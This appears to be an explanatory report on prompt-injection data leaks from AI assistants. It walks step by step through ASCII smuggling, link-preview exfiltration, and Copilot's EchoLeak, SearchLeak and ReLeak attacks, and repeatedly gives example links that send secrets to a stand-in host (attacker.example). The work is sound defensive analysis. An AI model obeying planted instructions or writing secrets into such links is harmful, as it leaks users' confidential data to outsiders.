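### What a click sends

Suppose an employee's mailbox contains a one-time login code, `ABC-123`, and a planted message controls the assistant's answer. The answer ends with a link labeled "View the full summary" that points to `https://attacker.example/report?c=ABC-123`.

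When the employee clicks, the code goes to the attacker's server as part of the address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly log the addresses visitors request, so the attacker needs no special software to collect the code.

The attacker's server has the code before the browser displays anything, so the leak succeeds whether the server returns an error or a convincing summary. Encryption doesn't prevent this, because it protects the request only on its way to the server, which the attacker runs.

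The secret could also be part of the path, as in `attacker.example/report/ABC-123`. Many servers accept addresses several thousand characters long, which is enough for a short email once the model replaces the spaces with plus signs.

Hovering over the link shows its address, as in the Slack AI demonstration, and an employee who has just received the secret code `ABC-123` might recognise it there. Attackers can make the code harder to spot by writing it in characters that the screen does not show.

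### Letters that nobody can see

Computers store text as numbers, and the Unicode standard determines which number means which character. The letter A is U+0041, written in hexadecimal (base 16). Unicode also has a set of "tag" characters that mirrors ASCII, the basic set of English letters, digits and punctuation marks. Graves (2026), in *Reverse CAPTCHA*, gives the rule:

tag character = U+E0000 + ordinary character

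The tag counterpart of A is therefore U+E0041. The hyphen, U+002D, becomes U+E002D, and the digit 1, U+0031, becomes U+E0031. Subtracting E0000 from each number recovers the hidden text.

Unicode's designers first meant tag characters to mark the language of a text and later reused them in some emoji. Programs that don't support them normally display nothing, not even a gap. Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* lists the code for each character in one hidden text. An invisible g appears as E0067, "TAG LATIN SMALL LETTER G", while the closing bracket after the hidden text is the ordinary 005D.

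In January 2024, Riley Goodside, who had helped to publicise prompt injection in 2022, found that language models can read this text. Goodside pasted a harmless-looking passage with hidden instructions into ChatGPT, which created an image as instructed. According to *ASCII Smuggler Tool*, on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, the models' training data apparently included tag characters. Rehberger's tool converts text to tag characters and back.

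Models can both read and write tag characters, so an attacker can use them to hide instructions in a planted message or a stolen secret in an answer. This technique is called ASCII smuggling. It works well for hiding a secret in a link. An answer could display the full address, `attacker.example/report/` followed by `ABC-123` in tag characters, and the employee would see only the harmless part.

The disguise is imperfect, because browsers rewrite unusual characters as percent codes before they send an address. An invisible A becomes `%F3%A0%81%81`, so the seven characters of the dummy code become 84. An employee who hovers over the link may see the long string and become suspicious, but could not recognise the dummy code in it.

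### The 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot

Rehberger used ASCII smuggling in an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that began with an email. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes the attack in these steps:

1. The attacker sends the victim an email that contains instructions for Copilot. A shared document would also do.
2. The victim asks Copilot about it, for example to list the key points.
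3. Copilot follows the instructions and searches the victim's mailbox for a different email.
4. Copilot writes the contents of that email in tag characters at the end of a link to the attacker's server, and invites the victim to click.
5. The victim clicks, and the attacker decodes the text from the server's log.

In one demonstration, Copilot searched for the confirmation codes that Slack sends by email when someone logs in. In another, it found sales figures.

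The search in step 3 makes the attacker's task much easier. In the Slack AI demonstration, the attacker had to wait for the victim to ask about the right secret. Here the victim asked only about the attacker's email, and the attacker chose what Copilot searched for next. Rehberger expected Copilot to follow instructions in an email, because no known method reliably prevents this, but he was surprised that those instructions could also make it run a new search without asking the user.

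Copilot needed an example to imitate for step 4, so Rehberger's email included a short greeting already written in tag characters.

The attack also needed a click because Microsoft had closed an easier route the year before. Bing Chat, which later became Copilot, used to load images from any address the model wrote, and the image request could carry data in the same way.

Rehberger calls the attack reliable but doesn't say how many attempts failed. The login codes may be less valuable than they look because, unlike sales figures, they usually expire within minutes and may require a password too.

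An attacker could also target one person with the email. Copilot has the user's name, job title and manager, so the attacker can instruct it to behave normally unless, say, the chief executive is asking. Rehberger (2024) calls this a conditional prompt injection in *Trust No AI*, a survey of such attacks.

Microsoft took several months to deal with the problem. On 17 January 2024, Rehberger reported only that Copilot was vulnerable to ASCII smuggling, and Microsoft closed the report a day later as low severity. That decision was defensible for ASCII smuggling alone, since invisible characters do no harm until something sends them to an attacker. Rehberger replied that they would matter as part of a longer attack, received no answer, and submitted that attack on 10 February.

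Microsoft opened a case three days later. In April it asked for time until the end of May, and in mid-May it was still working on what it called a comprehensive fix. By 2 July, the attack no longer worked for Rehberger. He presented it at a conference on 24 August. The blog post followed on 26 August, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Exposes User Data Risks*.

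Nobody outside Microsoft knows exactly what it changed. Rehberger asked for details and got no reply. He had advised Microsoft to stop displaying tag characters, to stop running searches automatically and, ideally, to stop showing clickable links. Copilot seemed to have stopped showing links, which was the only visible change. That would have been enough to break step 5, but Copilot could still have run searches on an attacker's behalf and written invisible text. Amazon fixed a similar problem in its workplace assistant, Amazon Q for Business, by no longer displaying links.

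### Which products remove invisible characters?

The best comparison of products comes from the security company FireTail, which tested six assistants in 2025. In January 2026, it tried a related method that hides text in an emoji. Unicode has 256 invisible "variation selectors", which normally choose between versions of a character, and each can stand for one byte of hidden text.

| Product | Followed text in tag characters (2025) | Followed text hidden in an emoji (2026) |
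|---|---|---|
| Gemini | Yes | Yes |
| Grok | Yes | Yes, on the second attempt |
| DeepSeek | Yes | No |
| ChatGPT | No | No |
| Claude | No | No |
| Microsoft Copilot | No | Not reported |
| Meta AI | Not reported | No |

The 2025 results come from Tom's Guide's *Researcher finds security flaw in Gemini*, which says that ChatGPT, Claude and Copilot clean the text they receive. The 2026 results come from FireTail (2026).

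Gemini matters most here because it can read its user's email and calendar. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, a set of notes by vict0ni, who did the 2025 work, describes a calendar invitation with the visible title "Meeting" and more text in invisible tag characters. The person invited sees only "Meeting", but Gemini also reads the hidden text.

According to Cybersecurity News, FireTail reported this to Google on 18 September 2025, and Google replied that it would take no action. BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability* also reported the refusal. The January 2026 result suggests that Google had not added a general filter for invisible text by then.

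Claude's place in the table needs a qualification, because Anthropic's programming agent, Claude Code, obeyed instructions written in tag characters in a demonstration that Rehberger published in June 2025. Anthropic does not regard this as a security vulnerability, according to Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*. Graves also found that Claude models could decode tag characters when a program contacted them directly. The most likely explanation is that Anthropic filters these characters in its chat product but not in the interface that developers use, though none of the three tests compared the two. A company that builds its own Slack bot on a Claude model should therefore not rely on FireTail's result.

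Graves ran the most detailed of these tests. He added an invisible instruction to give a particular wrong answer to each of 30 trivia questions, then collected 8,308 answers from five models released in 2024 and 2025. Without help, the models obeyed at most 1.1% of the time. When they could run code, which makes the instruction easy to decode, they still obeyed only 0% to 11% of the time.

Models often obeyed the hidden instructions only when the developer's standing instructions also told them that the text contained a hidden message. Claude Opus 4 then obeyed instructions written in tag characters every time if it could run code. OpenAI's GPT-5.2 almost never obeyed instructions in tag characters, but it followed about 70% of those written in a different invisible code.

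An attacker who can only send an email cannot change the developer's instructions, so Graves's low figures are closer to that attacker's chances of success. Graves didn't test attacks like Rehberger's, in which the email itself gave Copilot examples of the code, so the figures may still be too low for those.

The code that worked on GPT-5.2 uses two invisible characters, one for 0 and one for 1. Rehberger built a similar one. In Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits*, the letter A, which is 01000001 in binary, becomes a row of eight invisible mathematical symbols. A filter that removes only tag characters would miss it. The code is wasteful, however, especially in an address:

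| How the letter A is written | Characters in the answer | Characters in the address the browser sends |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary letter | 1 | 1 |
| Tag character | 1, invisible | 12 |
| Rehberger's binary code | 8, invisible | 72 |

If a server accepts addresses of up to 8,000 characters, an attacker could receive about 660 letters encoded as tag characters, or about 110 in the binary code, which is still more than enough for a password.

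Deleting every invisible character would cause display problems, because several Indian scripts and many emoji need some of them. Graves therefore recommends removing tag characters and looking for the suspicious patterns that the binary codes produce.

The FireTail and Graves tests covered hidden instructions that a model reads. A product could pass them and still let its model write a secret in invisible characters, so a filter has to check the model's answers as well as incoming text. Even a perfect filter for invisible characters would not stop leaks like the one from Slack AI, because the link that leaked the key contained none of them.

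### How a preview replaces the click

When someone posts a link in Slack, a small box with the page's title and perhaps a picture appears under the message. Developers call this unfurling, and it requires fetching the page to build the preview.

Messaging services differ in which computer fetches the linked page to build a preview. In iMessage and WhatsApp, the sender's device builds the preview and sends it with the message, according to MacRumors' *Link Previews in Popular Messaging Apps May Lead to Security Vulnerabilities* (2020). In some other apps, the recipient's device opened the link in the background, which worried researchers because a stranger could make someone's phone contact any server.

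Slack's servers fetch the page, so Slack can build a preview once and show it to everyone in the channel, and the page's owner doesn't learn the network address of anyone who reads the message. A bot also has no phone or desktop app to build the preview, since it is usually a program on a server that sends its text to Slack.

For an address that contains a secret, the arrangement is harmful. Suppose an employee asks a bot to summarise a document that contains planted instructions, and the bot has the dummy code in its context:

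1. The bot writes a reply that includes `attacker.example/report?c=ABC-123` and posts it in a channel.
2. Slack detects an address in the new message.
3. One of Slack's servers requests that address in order to build a preview.
4. The attacker's server logs the request, including `c=ABC-123`.
5. Slack shows a preview if the server returned a usable page.

The attacker has the code after step 4, possibly before anyone has read the reply. Security specialists call this a zero-click attack. Someone still has to use the bot while the planted text is in its context, but ordinary use is enough.

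The employer may see nothing unusual on its network either. The request goes from Slack's servers to the attacker's, so a web filter on the employee's laptop cannot block it. Deleting the message a minute later would not help, nor would posting it in a channel with only one member. By default, Slack fetches links even in messages that a bot shows to a single person.

Rehberger had listed link previews among the risks of chatbots in 2023 and explained the preview risk fully in August 2024, in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. In a simple test described there, Rehberger had a program post a link in Slack, and the linked server logged a visit from a program that identified itself as "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0". This showed that Slack fetches links posted by programs, although Rehberger did not attack any particular company's bot.

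The danger of link previews was not obvious even to specialists. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024), published on 21 August, the day after PromptArmor published its attack on Slack AI, describes a vulnerability that Willison "hadn't thought about before". Previews had been common for years, and they were fairly safe as long as people wrote the messages, because people rarely paste their own passwords into a stranger's web address. But instructions planted in a message can make a language model put a user's password into such an address.

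A developer can turn previews off for each message a bot posts to Slack, with one setting for web pages and another for media such as images. Slack leaves both on unless the developer changes them.

### The flaw in Anthropic's Slack server

Anthropic had not changed them in a free sample server that lets an agent read and post messages in Slack. It was one of several sample servers that Anthropic published along with the MCP standard, and it is separate from the MCP server that Slack now runs itself.

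In 2025, Rehberger demonstrated an attack on Anthropic's server with Claude Desktop, Anthropic's app for personal computers. The user asked Claude to summarise a document and post the summary for colleagues. The document contained instructions to read the last message in another Slack channel and add it to a link in the post. Claude posted the link in a private channel, Slack fetched it, and the message from the other channel appeared in the log of Rehberger's server.

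The other demonstration used Claude Code and stole an API key from a developer's computer rather than data from Slack. The developer asked the agent to analyse a code file that contained instructions in tag characters. The agent then opened a file where programmers often keep API keys and used Slack to post a link containing a key. If the link is to an image, Slack may send the key more than once, because up to three of its programs request the image's address.

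Link previews can leak data even when Anthropic's server is limited to a single private channel, because the attacker doesn't need to read the channel. A careful administrator might let an agent post there without approval, thinking it safe because only trusted colleagues can read the messages. Rehberger also worries that people who begin by approving each action gradually stop checking after seeing nothing go wrong.

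Rehberger reported the flaw to Anthropic on 27 May 2025. Two days later, Anthropic archived the server, so the code is still available but Anthropic no longer maintains it. Rehberger couldn't tell whether his report had prompted this. Anthropic had retired many of its sample servers around the same time and had no plans to fix security flaws in them. It did not object to publication.

The flaw is listed as CVE-2025-34072 in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. The security company VulnCheck assigned the number, and its *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* says the flaw affects all default installations. Neither Rehberger's advisory nor the entry in the US government's vulnerability database, NVD's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025), lists a fixed version, so anyone who still uses the archived program has to fix it themselves. Rehberger's suggested patch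 adds two lines, one for each of Slack's preview settings, to the functions that post messages and replies.

VulnCheck scored the flaw at 9.3 out of 10, which counts as critical. That score deserves some caution because Rehberger, who found the flaw, gave it 7.5, and the government database lists VulnCheck's score but had no assessment of its own. Three chatbots that Rehberger asked gave scores between 8.7 and 9.3.

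Part of the difference may come from how one counts the damage. VulnCheck's score assumes that an attacker could severely alter or disable other systems as well as read data from them. The flaw itself only copies data, though an intruder with a stolen key might also alter or disable systems, depending on what the key gives access to. VulnCheck also assumes that the attack requires no action by the user. That is true of the preview, but somebody must first give the agent a planted document.

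The number of companies at risk is also uncertain. Rehberger suggested that there might be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations, because the server had more than 14,000 weekly downloads at the time of the advisory. Weekly downloads are a poor guide to the number of installations, since automated systems often download the same program again each time they run. Rehberger also notes that the danger depends on how a company uses the server. It is greatest when an outsider can guess where to plant the text and what will make the agent post.

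### PromptArmor's test of agents and messaging apps

In February 2026, PromptArmor tried to find out how common the problem was by building a website that recorded preview requests and inviting people to try it with whatever agent and messaging app they used. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes the test.

A visitor had their agent write a link to the test site with some data in the address. If a messaging service fetched the link, the site displayed the request and the data it contained. In PromptArmor's example, the data were a name and an API key. Each service's program identifies itself when it fetches a link, so the request showed which service had fetched it but not which agent had written it. Visitors could claim a request and name their agent. They could also report combinations of agent and messaging service that had produced no preview.

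PromptArmor's main example was OpenClaw, a popular agent program that people instruct through messaging apps. With the default settings, conversations with OpenClaw on Telegram were exposed because Telegram would fetch any link in the agent's replies, including one that a planted message had made the agent write. Turning off link previews in OpenClaw's configuration file stopped the leak. The Hacker News (2026) reported that the same method could work through Discord.

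Microsoft Teams also leaked data when used with assistants built in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for making custom assistants, and Slack did so with certain bots, according to Apostol in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*.

These results are good evidence that the leak is possible in several popular products, since a logged request containing the test data is hard to explain any other way. We can't tell from them how common the leak is, because the participants volunteered and probably included many who already suspected a problem. PromptArmor's chart of the services that fetched the most links partly reflects which services its visitors used.

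Reports that a combination was safe are even weaker evidence, because a visitor might have turned previews off earlier and forgotten, or the agent might have declined to write the link. The agents' names also come from visitors' reports, and the same bot can behave differently at two companies whose administrators chose different settings.

PromptArmor's test also left out the hardest step for an attacker, which is getting the agent to write the link. A visitor could ask their own agent to write it, whereas a real attacker has to plant text that the agent may ignore. A leak in the test therefore means that nothing would stop the data once the agent had written the link, but the test didn't measure how often an attack would get that far.

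Apostol reports that PromptArmor considers the messaging platforms largely responsible for fixing the problem. In its own article, PromptArmor divides the responsibility more evenly. It asks messaging services to let developers control previews, perhaps separately for each channel, and asks agent developers to use those controls or offer them to their users. Slack already had such controls in 2024, so when a new bot leaks data through Slack's previews, it is usually because its developer left them on.

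## Why did Microsoft 365 Copilot leak again after each repair?

Microsoft 365 Copilot searches Teams chats, email and files, so a stranger's email can end up in the same context as a password that a colleague posted in a chat. Its leaks are better documented than those of any other workplace assistant. In Rehberger's 2024 attack, Copilot hid stolen email text in a link. Researchers then disclosed EchoLeak in June 2025, SearchLeak in June 2026 and ReLeak on 3 December 2026.

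Microsoft repaired each leak. Each attack had to get past several defences in a row, so Microsoft could stop it by closing any one of the gaps it used. The later attacks suggest that Microsoft left some of the other gaps open.

### EchoLeak begins with an email that never mentions Copilot

In January 2025, Aim Labs found EchoLeak and reported it to Microsoft, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025). Aim Labs published the details in June, after Microsoft repaired the flaw. EchoLeak is catalogued as CVE-2025-32711 and has a severity of 9.3 out of 10, according to BeyondMachines' *Critical vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot AI called EchoLeak enabled data exfiltration*.

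The attack began with the long email described earlier, which used "RAG spraying" to match questions on many subjects. The email could come from any address.

Microsoft's first defence was an injection classifier, a program meant to catch instructions planted in text before they reach the model. Microsoft calls such instructions cross-prompt injection attacks, or XPIA. Aim Labs got past the classifier with an email that addressed its instructions to the employee and never mentioned Copilot, assistants or AI, so it looked like one person telling another how to do something.

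Office email is full of instructions, so a classifier that blocked every message asking its reader to copy a number into a form would block a lot of legitimate mail. An instruction that is harmless to a human reader can be dangerous when Copilot reads it. Ravia thinks malicious emails of this kind are hard but not impossible to detect, and adds that developers have few good collections of real attacks for training a classifier.

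The email requested the most sensitive item in the model's context, so the attacker did not have to name a particular secret. In the Slack AI demonstration, by contrast, the attacker had to guess which service the victim would ask about. Aim Labs calls it an "LLM scope violation" when an outsider's text directs the model to internal data.

### A link format that the filter missed

Copilot also removed links to outside websites from its answers before the employee could click them. This may have been part of the repair after Rehberger's attack.

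The filter had a gap. Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, which has more than one way to write a link. In the usual form, the address comes directly after the visible text:

`[Launch plan](wiki.example/launch)`

A reference-style link puts the address elsewhere in the text and connects the two with a label:

`[Launch plan][plan]`

`[plan]: wiki.example/launch`

Both forms display the same clickable words. Copilot's filter recognised only the first, so Aim Labs had the model write the second. This was already enough for a one-click leak, much like the one from Slack AI.

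Aim Labs then replaced the link with an image, which would not need a click because a browser normally requests an image as soon as it displays the answer. A Markdown image looks like a link with an exclamation mark in front, and it can also use the reference style. The filter missed reference-style images too.

### The content security policy, and a Teams server that fetched outside pages

Copilot's content security policy still stopped the browser from loading the image. A website sends this kind of policy to the browser with a page. It lists the places from which the browser may load images, scripts and other parts of the page, and the browser blocks requests for them to anywhere else.

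Copilot's policy allowed images from about 30 addresses, most of them Microsoft's. The list did not include `attacker.example`, but some entries covered whole families of sites. For instance, `*.sharepoint.com` allowed images from any site on SharePoint, Microsoft's service for shared documents, including a site that an attacker had set up.

Aim Labs therefore looked for a permitted server that would pass the data on. A browser loading an image won't run a program from the page it receives, so the server had to make the next request itself. SharePoint had a function that did this, but the victim first had to accept an invitation to the attacker's site, and few employees would accept one from a site they didn't know.

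Teams had a similar function with no such condition. It fetched outside web pages, perhaps to build link previews, and anyone could specify which page. With a dummy key, the last part of the attack worked like this:

1. Copilot's answer contained an image whose address was on a Teams server. Inside that address was a second one, `attacker.example/DUMMY-KEY`.
2. The browser found the Teams server on the list of permitted addresses and sent the request.
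3. The Teams server read the second address and fetched it.
4. The attacker's server logged the request, including `DUMMY-KEY`.

The browser complied with the content security policy throughout. The policy controls where the browser sends its own requests, but not what a permitted server does after receiving one.

The employee would also have had trouble finding the cause. Copilot normally cites the emails it uses, but the attacker had written in the planted email that its "recipient" should never refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot did not cite it. The attacker had planned this omission, whereas nobody could say for certain why Slack AI did not cite the planted message in the earlier case.

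Aim Labs called EchoLeak the first zero-click attack on a major AI application. Several earlier attacks had also loaded images automatically, so whether the claim is true depends on how "zero-click" is defined. Ravia contrasts EchoLeak with attacks that required the user to point the assistant at the hostile content, or that could steal only certain data. By that standard, EchoLeak went further than Rehberger's attack, in which the victim had to ask about the attacker's email and then click.

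Ravia also says that, as far as Aim Labs knew, no administrator's setting would have prevented the leak. Microsoft confirmed that no customers were affected. Aim Labs gives no success rate and does not describe what Microsoft changed. Microsoft might, for example, have changed the filter to recognise reference-style links or closed the Teams function. Either change would have stopped the zero-click attack, but they would have left very different gaps.

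### SearchLeak puts the instruction in a link

A year later, the data-security company Varonis found an attack that needed no planted email. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes the attack, which targeted Copilot Enterprise Search, the part of Copilot focused on finding company email, meetings and files.

Copilot's search page, like many others, accepted a query as part of its web address. This lets colleagues share searches, but Copilot treated the query as a prompt and followed any instructions in it. An attacker could therefore put instructions in a link to the page and send the link by email, Teams or any other service. When the victim clicked it, Copilot carried out the instructions as if the victim had typed them.

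The attack was no longer zero-click, but its instructions didn't have to rank above genuine messages to appear in the search results, and they ran immediately instead of only when the user asked a suitable question. They could also specify what Copilot searched for. A classifier that examined only retrieved emails would have missed these instructions, though Taler doesn't say whether Microsoft's classifier also examined queries.

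The link led to a genuine Microsoft address, so a cautious employee had little reason to distrust it and an email filter had little basis for blocking it. Taler advises employees to inspect Microsoft links for long, encoded queries, but this advice is hard to follow because many ordinary links are also long and unreadable.

After the click, the attack used two older kinds of web flaw. Suppose the victim has an email with the title "Your code is ABC-123":

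1. Copilot searched the mailbox, found the email and took its title.
2. It began to write an answer containing an image, with the title in the image's address.
3. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived and immediately requested the image.
4. Copilot finished the answer, and only then did Microsoft's software mark the whole text as code, so that the browser would show the image instruction as plain text instead of obeying it.

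The safety measure in step 4 came too late. Copilot showed its answers word by word so that people didn't have to wait, but the protection worked only on a complete answer. By the time the page was finished and looked safe, the request had already gone out. Programmers call this a race condition, meaning that the result depends on which of two events happens first.

The image request still had to satisfy the content security policy, so Varonis sent it to Bing's search-by-image function. Given the address of a picture, Bing's server downloads the picture to analyse it. Varonis supplied an address that contained the email's title, like `attacker.example/Your_code_is_ABC-123/img.png`. When Bing tried to download the picture, it sent the title to the attacker's server.

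This is the same as EchoLeak's last step, except that it uses Bing instead of Teams. The policy that Ravia published in 2025 already included `*.bing.com` among the entries for Microsoft's own image servers. Anyone who had read about the Teams function, at Microsoft or elsewhere, could have looked through the other entries for ones that also fetched outside addresses. After SearchLeak, Taler advised security teams to do this.

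The published example leaked only an email title. Taler emphasises titles because they sometimes contain one-time codes. Copilot also had access to the text of emails, calendar entries and files, but Varonis did not demonstrate leaking a long document, which an attacker would have had to fit into web addresses.

Varonis had first used the search-address trick in an attack called Reprompt on the consumer version of Copilot, which is a separate product. It was surprised that the trick also worked in the version for companies, where it had expected stronger protection. UNU's *The AI That Ratted Itself Out* describes Varonis's CoSnitch research, which was also on the consumer version.

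### How severe was one click?

Microsoft repaired SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824) in early June 2026, according to TechRadar. Published severity ratings range from medium to the maximum. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft scored it 6.5 out of 10 because the victim had to click, while the US government's National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5 because it judged that the victim did not have to do anything. Microsoft was right on that point, since nothing happened until the victim opened the link.

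Varonis nevertheless says that Microsoft gave SearchLeak a "max severity rating of critical", and TechRadar reports a score of 10 out of 10. Microsoft rates flaws in both words and numbers, and the two do not always match, so it could call SearchLeak critical and still score it 6.5. TechRadar may have taken "max severity" to mean the highest possible score.

A one-point difference for requiring a click seems about right if the attacker has a single target. The requirement matters less if the attacker can send the link to a thousand employees, because only one of them has to click it.

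### ReLeak returns to email and finds three exits

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim Labs became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, also found by this group.

All three started like EchoLeak. The attacker sent an email, the victim left it unopened, and Copilot retrieved it while answering an ordinary work question. The email again got past Microsoft's classifier. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* reports that Copilot did not obey blunt commands but followed instructions that looked like legitimate requests. The victim didn't have to approve anything.

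The first attack, CVE-2026-124115, used an image again. Copilot put confidential data into an image address in its answer, the browser loaded the image, and Bing passed the data to an outside server. Antipov (2026) points out in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* that SearchLeak sent data out in a similar way. With CVE-2026-124115, however, nobody had to click a link.

### A document that leaks after the conversation ends

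The second attack, CVE-2026-124132, depended on Copilot's newer ability to create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them to OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's storage services. The planted email made Copilot create a file containing a link with confidential data in its address. Microsoft's servers later processed the file in the background and fetched the link.

In Cato's tests, the data leaked one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the file. Closing the chat after noticing an odd answer would not have stopped the leak. Deleting the new file might have, but only if the employee knew about it and acted quickly.

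The accounts of ReLeak do not explain why the background process fetched the link. It may have been building a preview or checking the file for malware. The effect was the same as with link previews in Slack.

Copilot's content security policy applies to the page in the employee's browser, so it could not block this request, which came from a Microsoft server. A stricter list of permitted image addresses might have stopped EchoLeak and SearchLeak, but not this request.

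### Code that reached the internet from a closed machine

The third attack, CVE-2026-78501, used Copilot's code interpreter. When a question calls for calculation or a chart, the model can write and run a Python program. Running code written by a model is risky, so Microsoft runs it in a sandbox, an isolated environment intended to contain any damage.

Microsoft says it protects this sandbox in several ways. Each run starts on a fresh virtual machine (a simulated computer), separate from other sessions and from Copilot's main services. Microsoft then destroys the machine and any data on it. Limits on time, memory and disk space keep a program from using too much of the system. Software scans the running code for malicious patterns and ends the session if, for example, the code tries to open restricted files. The machines also "don't allow any inbound or outbound traffic", which Microsoft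 says prevents code from sending data to outside servers.

Cato's code sent data to an outside server anyway. None of the news accounts explains how the researchers got around the network block, so it is hard to judge whether this was a small configuration error or a deeper fault. The scanning evidently did not stop the request either. The other layers protect against different dangers. Destroying the machine, for example, prevents one customer's files from appearing in another customer's session, but it cannot recover data that has already been sent out.

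This was the most direct of the routes, since the attacker needed neither an image nor a Microsoft service to pass on the request. A program can also send much more data than fits in a web address. Microsoft first scored the flaw at 7.4 and later raised the score to 8.6, according to Antipov. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft also called the flaw critical, although 8.6 falls in the "high" range of the numerical scale.

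Like Cato, the research group Rubrik Zero Labs found a way out of Copilot's sandbox. In August 2026, it showed that a single Word document could break out of the sandbox into Azure, Microsoft's cloud service, according to *AI sandbox escape uncovered in Microsoft Copilot flaw* (Knight, 2026).

Companies can also give the code interpreter to assistants they build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio. Nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected those assistants, but it was worth checking because Microsoft describes the same isolation for all of them.

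### The five routes side by side

Microsoft received Cato's reports between 29 July and 20 August 2026 and repaired the code interpreter first. The table lists the three ReLeak attacks separately because each leaked data by a different route and had its own repair.

| Attack | Way in | Way out | Clicks | Repaired |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Email that Copilot retrieved | Image address, fetched by a Teams server | None | By June 2025 |
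| SearchLeak | Instructions in a link to Copilot's search page | Image address, fetched by Bing | One | Early June 2026 |
| ReLeak, image | Email that Copilot retrieved | Image address, fetched by Bing | None | 15 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, file | Email that Copilot retrieved | Link in a new file, fetched by Microsoft's background servers | None | 11 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, code | Email that Copilot retrieved | Request sent directly from the code sandbox | None | 17 September 2026 |

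Four of the five attacks came in through email, even though Microsoft had known since January 2025 that an email addressed to a human reader could get past its classifier. Microsoft may well have improved the classifier after that, but it did not block the finished version of any of the three later email attacks. Cato used AI agents to write test prompts, study Copilot's refusals and adjust the next attempt, so Copilot did refuse some prompts. The number of failed attempts is unknown, so the classifier may have made Cato's attack much harder or only slightly slower.

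Microsoft's repairs to the routes by which data left Copilot were also narrow, most clearly with Bing. It fixed SearchLeak in early June, but by 20 August Cato had reported another attack that sent data through Bing. The June repair may have stopped Copilot from obeying instructions in search addresses, or stopped images from loading too early, without changing how Bing fetched addresses. Alternatively, Microsoft may have closed one Bing function and Cato may have found another. Under either explanation, Copilot's page still accepted images from Bing, and part of Bing still fetched addresses chosen by an attacker.

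Microsoft took longest to close this route. It repaired the image attack 87 to 109 days after Cato reported it, depending on the exact report date, compared with 28 to 50 days for the code interpreter. Fixing the code interpreter first is defensible, because it could send data straight to an attacker and had no need for internet access. Bing's image search, by contrast, has to fetch outside pictures to work, and many people use it for reasons unrelated to Copilot. Still, Microsoft had already seen data leak this way in the spring.

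Microsoft could have made a broader repair by stopping Copilot from displaying images from addresses the model had written. EchoLeak, SearchLeak and the first ReLeak attack all needed the browser to load such an image, so all three would have failed, regardless of which Microsoft service could fetch the address. Users would have lost some legitimate images from their answers.

Copilot's filters looked for particular ways of embedding an image, and researchers kept finding others. Rehberger found the same weakness in another 2026 flaw, CVE-2026-24299. According to Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, Copilot removed ordinary image tags from a web page it had generated, but the page's style sheet, which controls its appearance, could still load a background image.

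The other two ReLeak attacks used abilities unrelated to displaying an answer, so even a complete ban on images would not have prevented them. Every time Microsoft gives Copilot a new ability, such as saving a file or running a program, it has to work out whether that ability can send data outside the company. Microsoft had done this for the code interpreter and had designed a network block to prevent such leaks, but the block failed. For new files, the weak point was a background service that opened links in documents. As with link previews, opening links automatically was much less of a problem when people wrote the text.

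### Has Microsoft made too little progress?

Cato concludes that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells security products for AI systems, so it benefits when customers think Microsoft's defences are inadequate. But the evidence supports part of the complaint. More than a year later, a planted email still worked by much the same trick, and an image address could still carry data out through a Microsoft server.

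But three new attacks in one summer do not prove that Copilot had become less secure. Cato's researchers knew the product well and used AI agents to run their tests, so they could probably try far more variations than in early 2025. Copilot is also a popular target. A less prominent assistant with worse flaws might have no published attacks because nobody has looked for them.

Microsoft also closed every route before anyone reported a theft. Cato knew of no affected customers or real attacks when it published ReLeak. This is reassuring but doesn't rule out theft, because victims would see few signs of such an attack and Cato can see only part of what happens at Microsoft's customers.

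Microsoft made the ReLeak repairs on its own servers, which protected all customers at once, including companies that are slow to update their software. Because customers had nothing to install, they also had little to examine. When Faisal wrote about ReLeak on 5 December, two of the three entries in the public vulnerability catalogue were still marked "reserved", with no description or score. A security team could learn that Microsoft had fixed the Bing route, but not whether it had closed one address or stopped Bing from passing on Copilot data altogether.

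## Why did access permissions not stop these leaks?

In the Slack AI demonstration and the later attacks on Copilot, the assistant used only material that the victim could already read. The permission check therefore worked correctly but did not stop the secret from leaving the company.

### What the permission check covers

Let R(u) be the set of everything that user u may read, including their email, their private channels and every public channel. When u asks a question, the assistant retrieves a set of items, C. The check confirms that

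C ⊆ R(u)

which means that u could have opened every retrieved item without the assistant's help.

In the Slack AI case, the key was in the victim's own private channel and the planted message was in a public one. The victim was allowed to read both, so both passed the permission check. The attacker was not allowed to read the key, but Slack had no reason to check the attacker's permissions because the attacker hadn't asked the assistant for anything.

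EchoLeak passed the same permission check even more easily. The victim can read an email as soon as it arrives, whoever sent it, so a stranger can add items to the set the victim can read without being able to read anything in that set.

The permission check doesn't consider who wrote an item or where the answer will go. An access list records who may read a message, but not whether the assistant should follow its author's instructions. Slack showed the answer only to the victim, but the answer contained a link to the attacker's server. To catch the leak, Slack would have had to check that whoever ran that server was also allowed to read the key.

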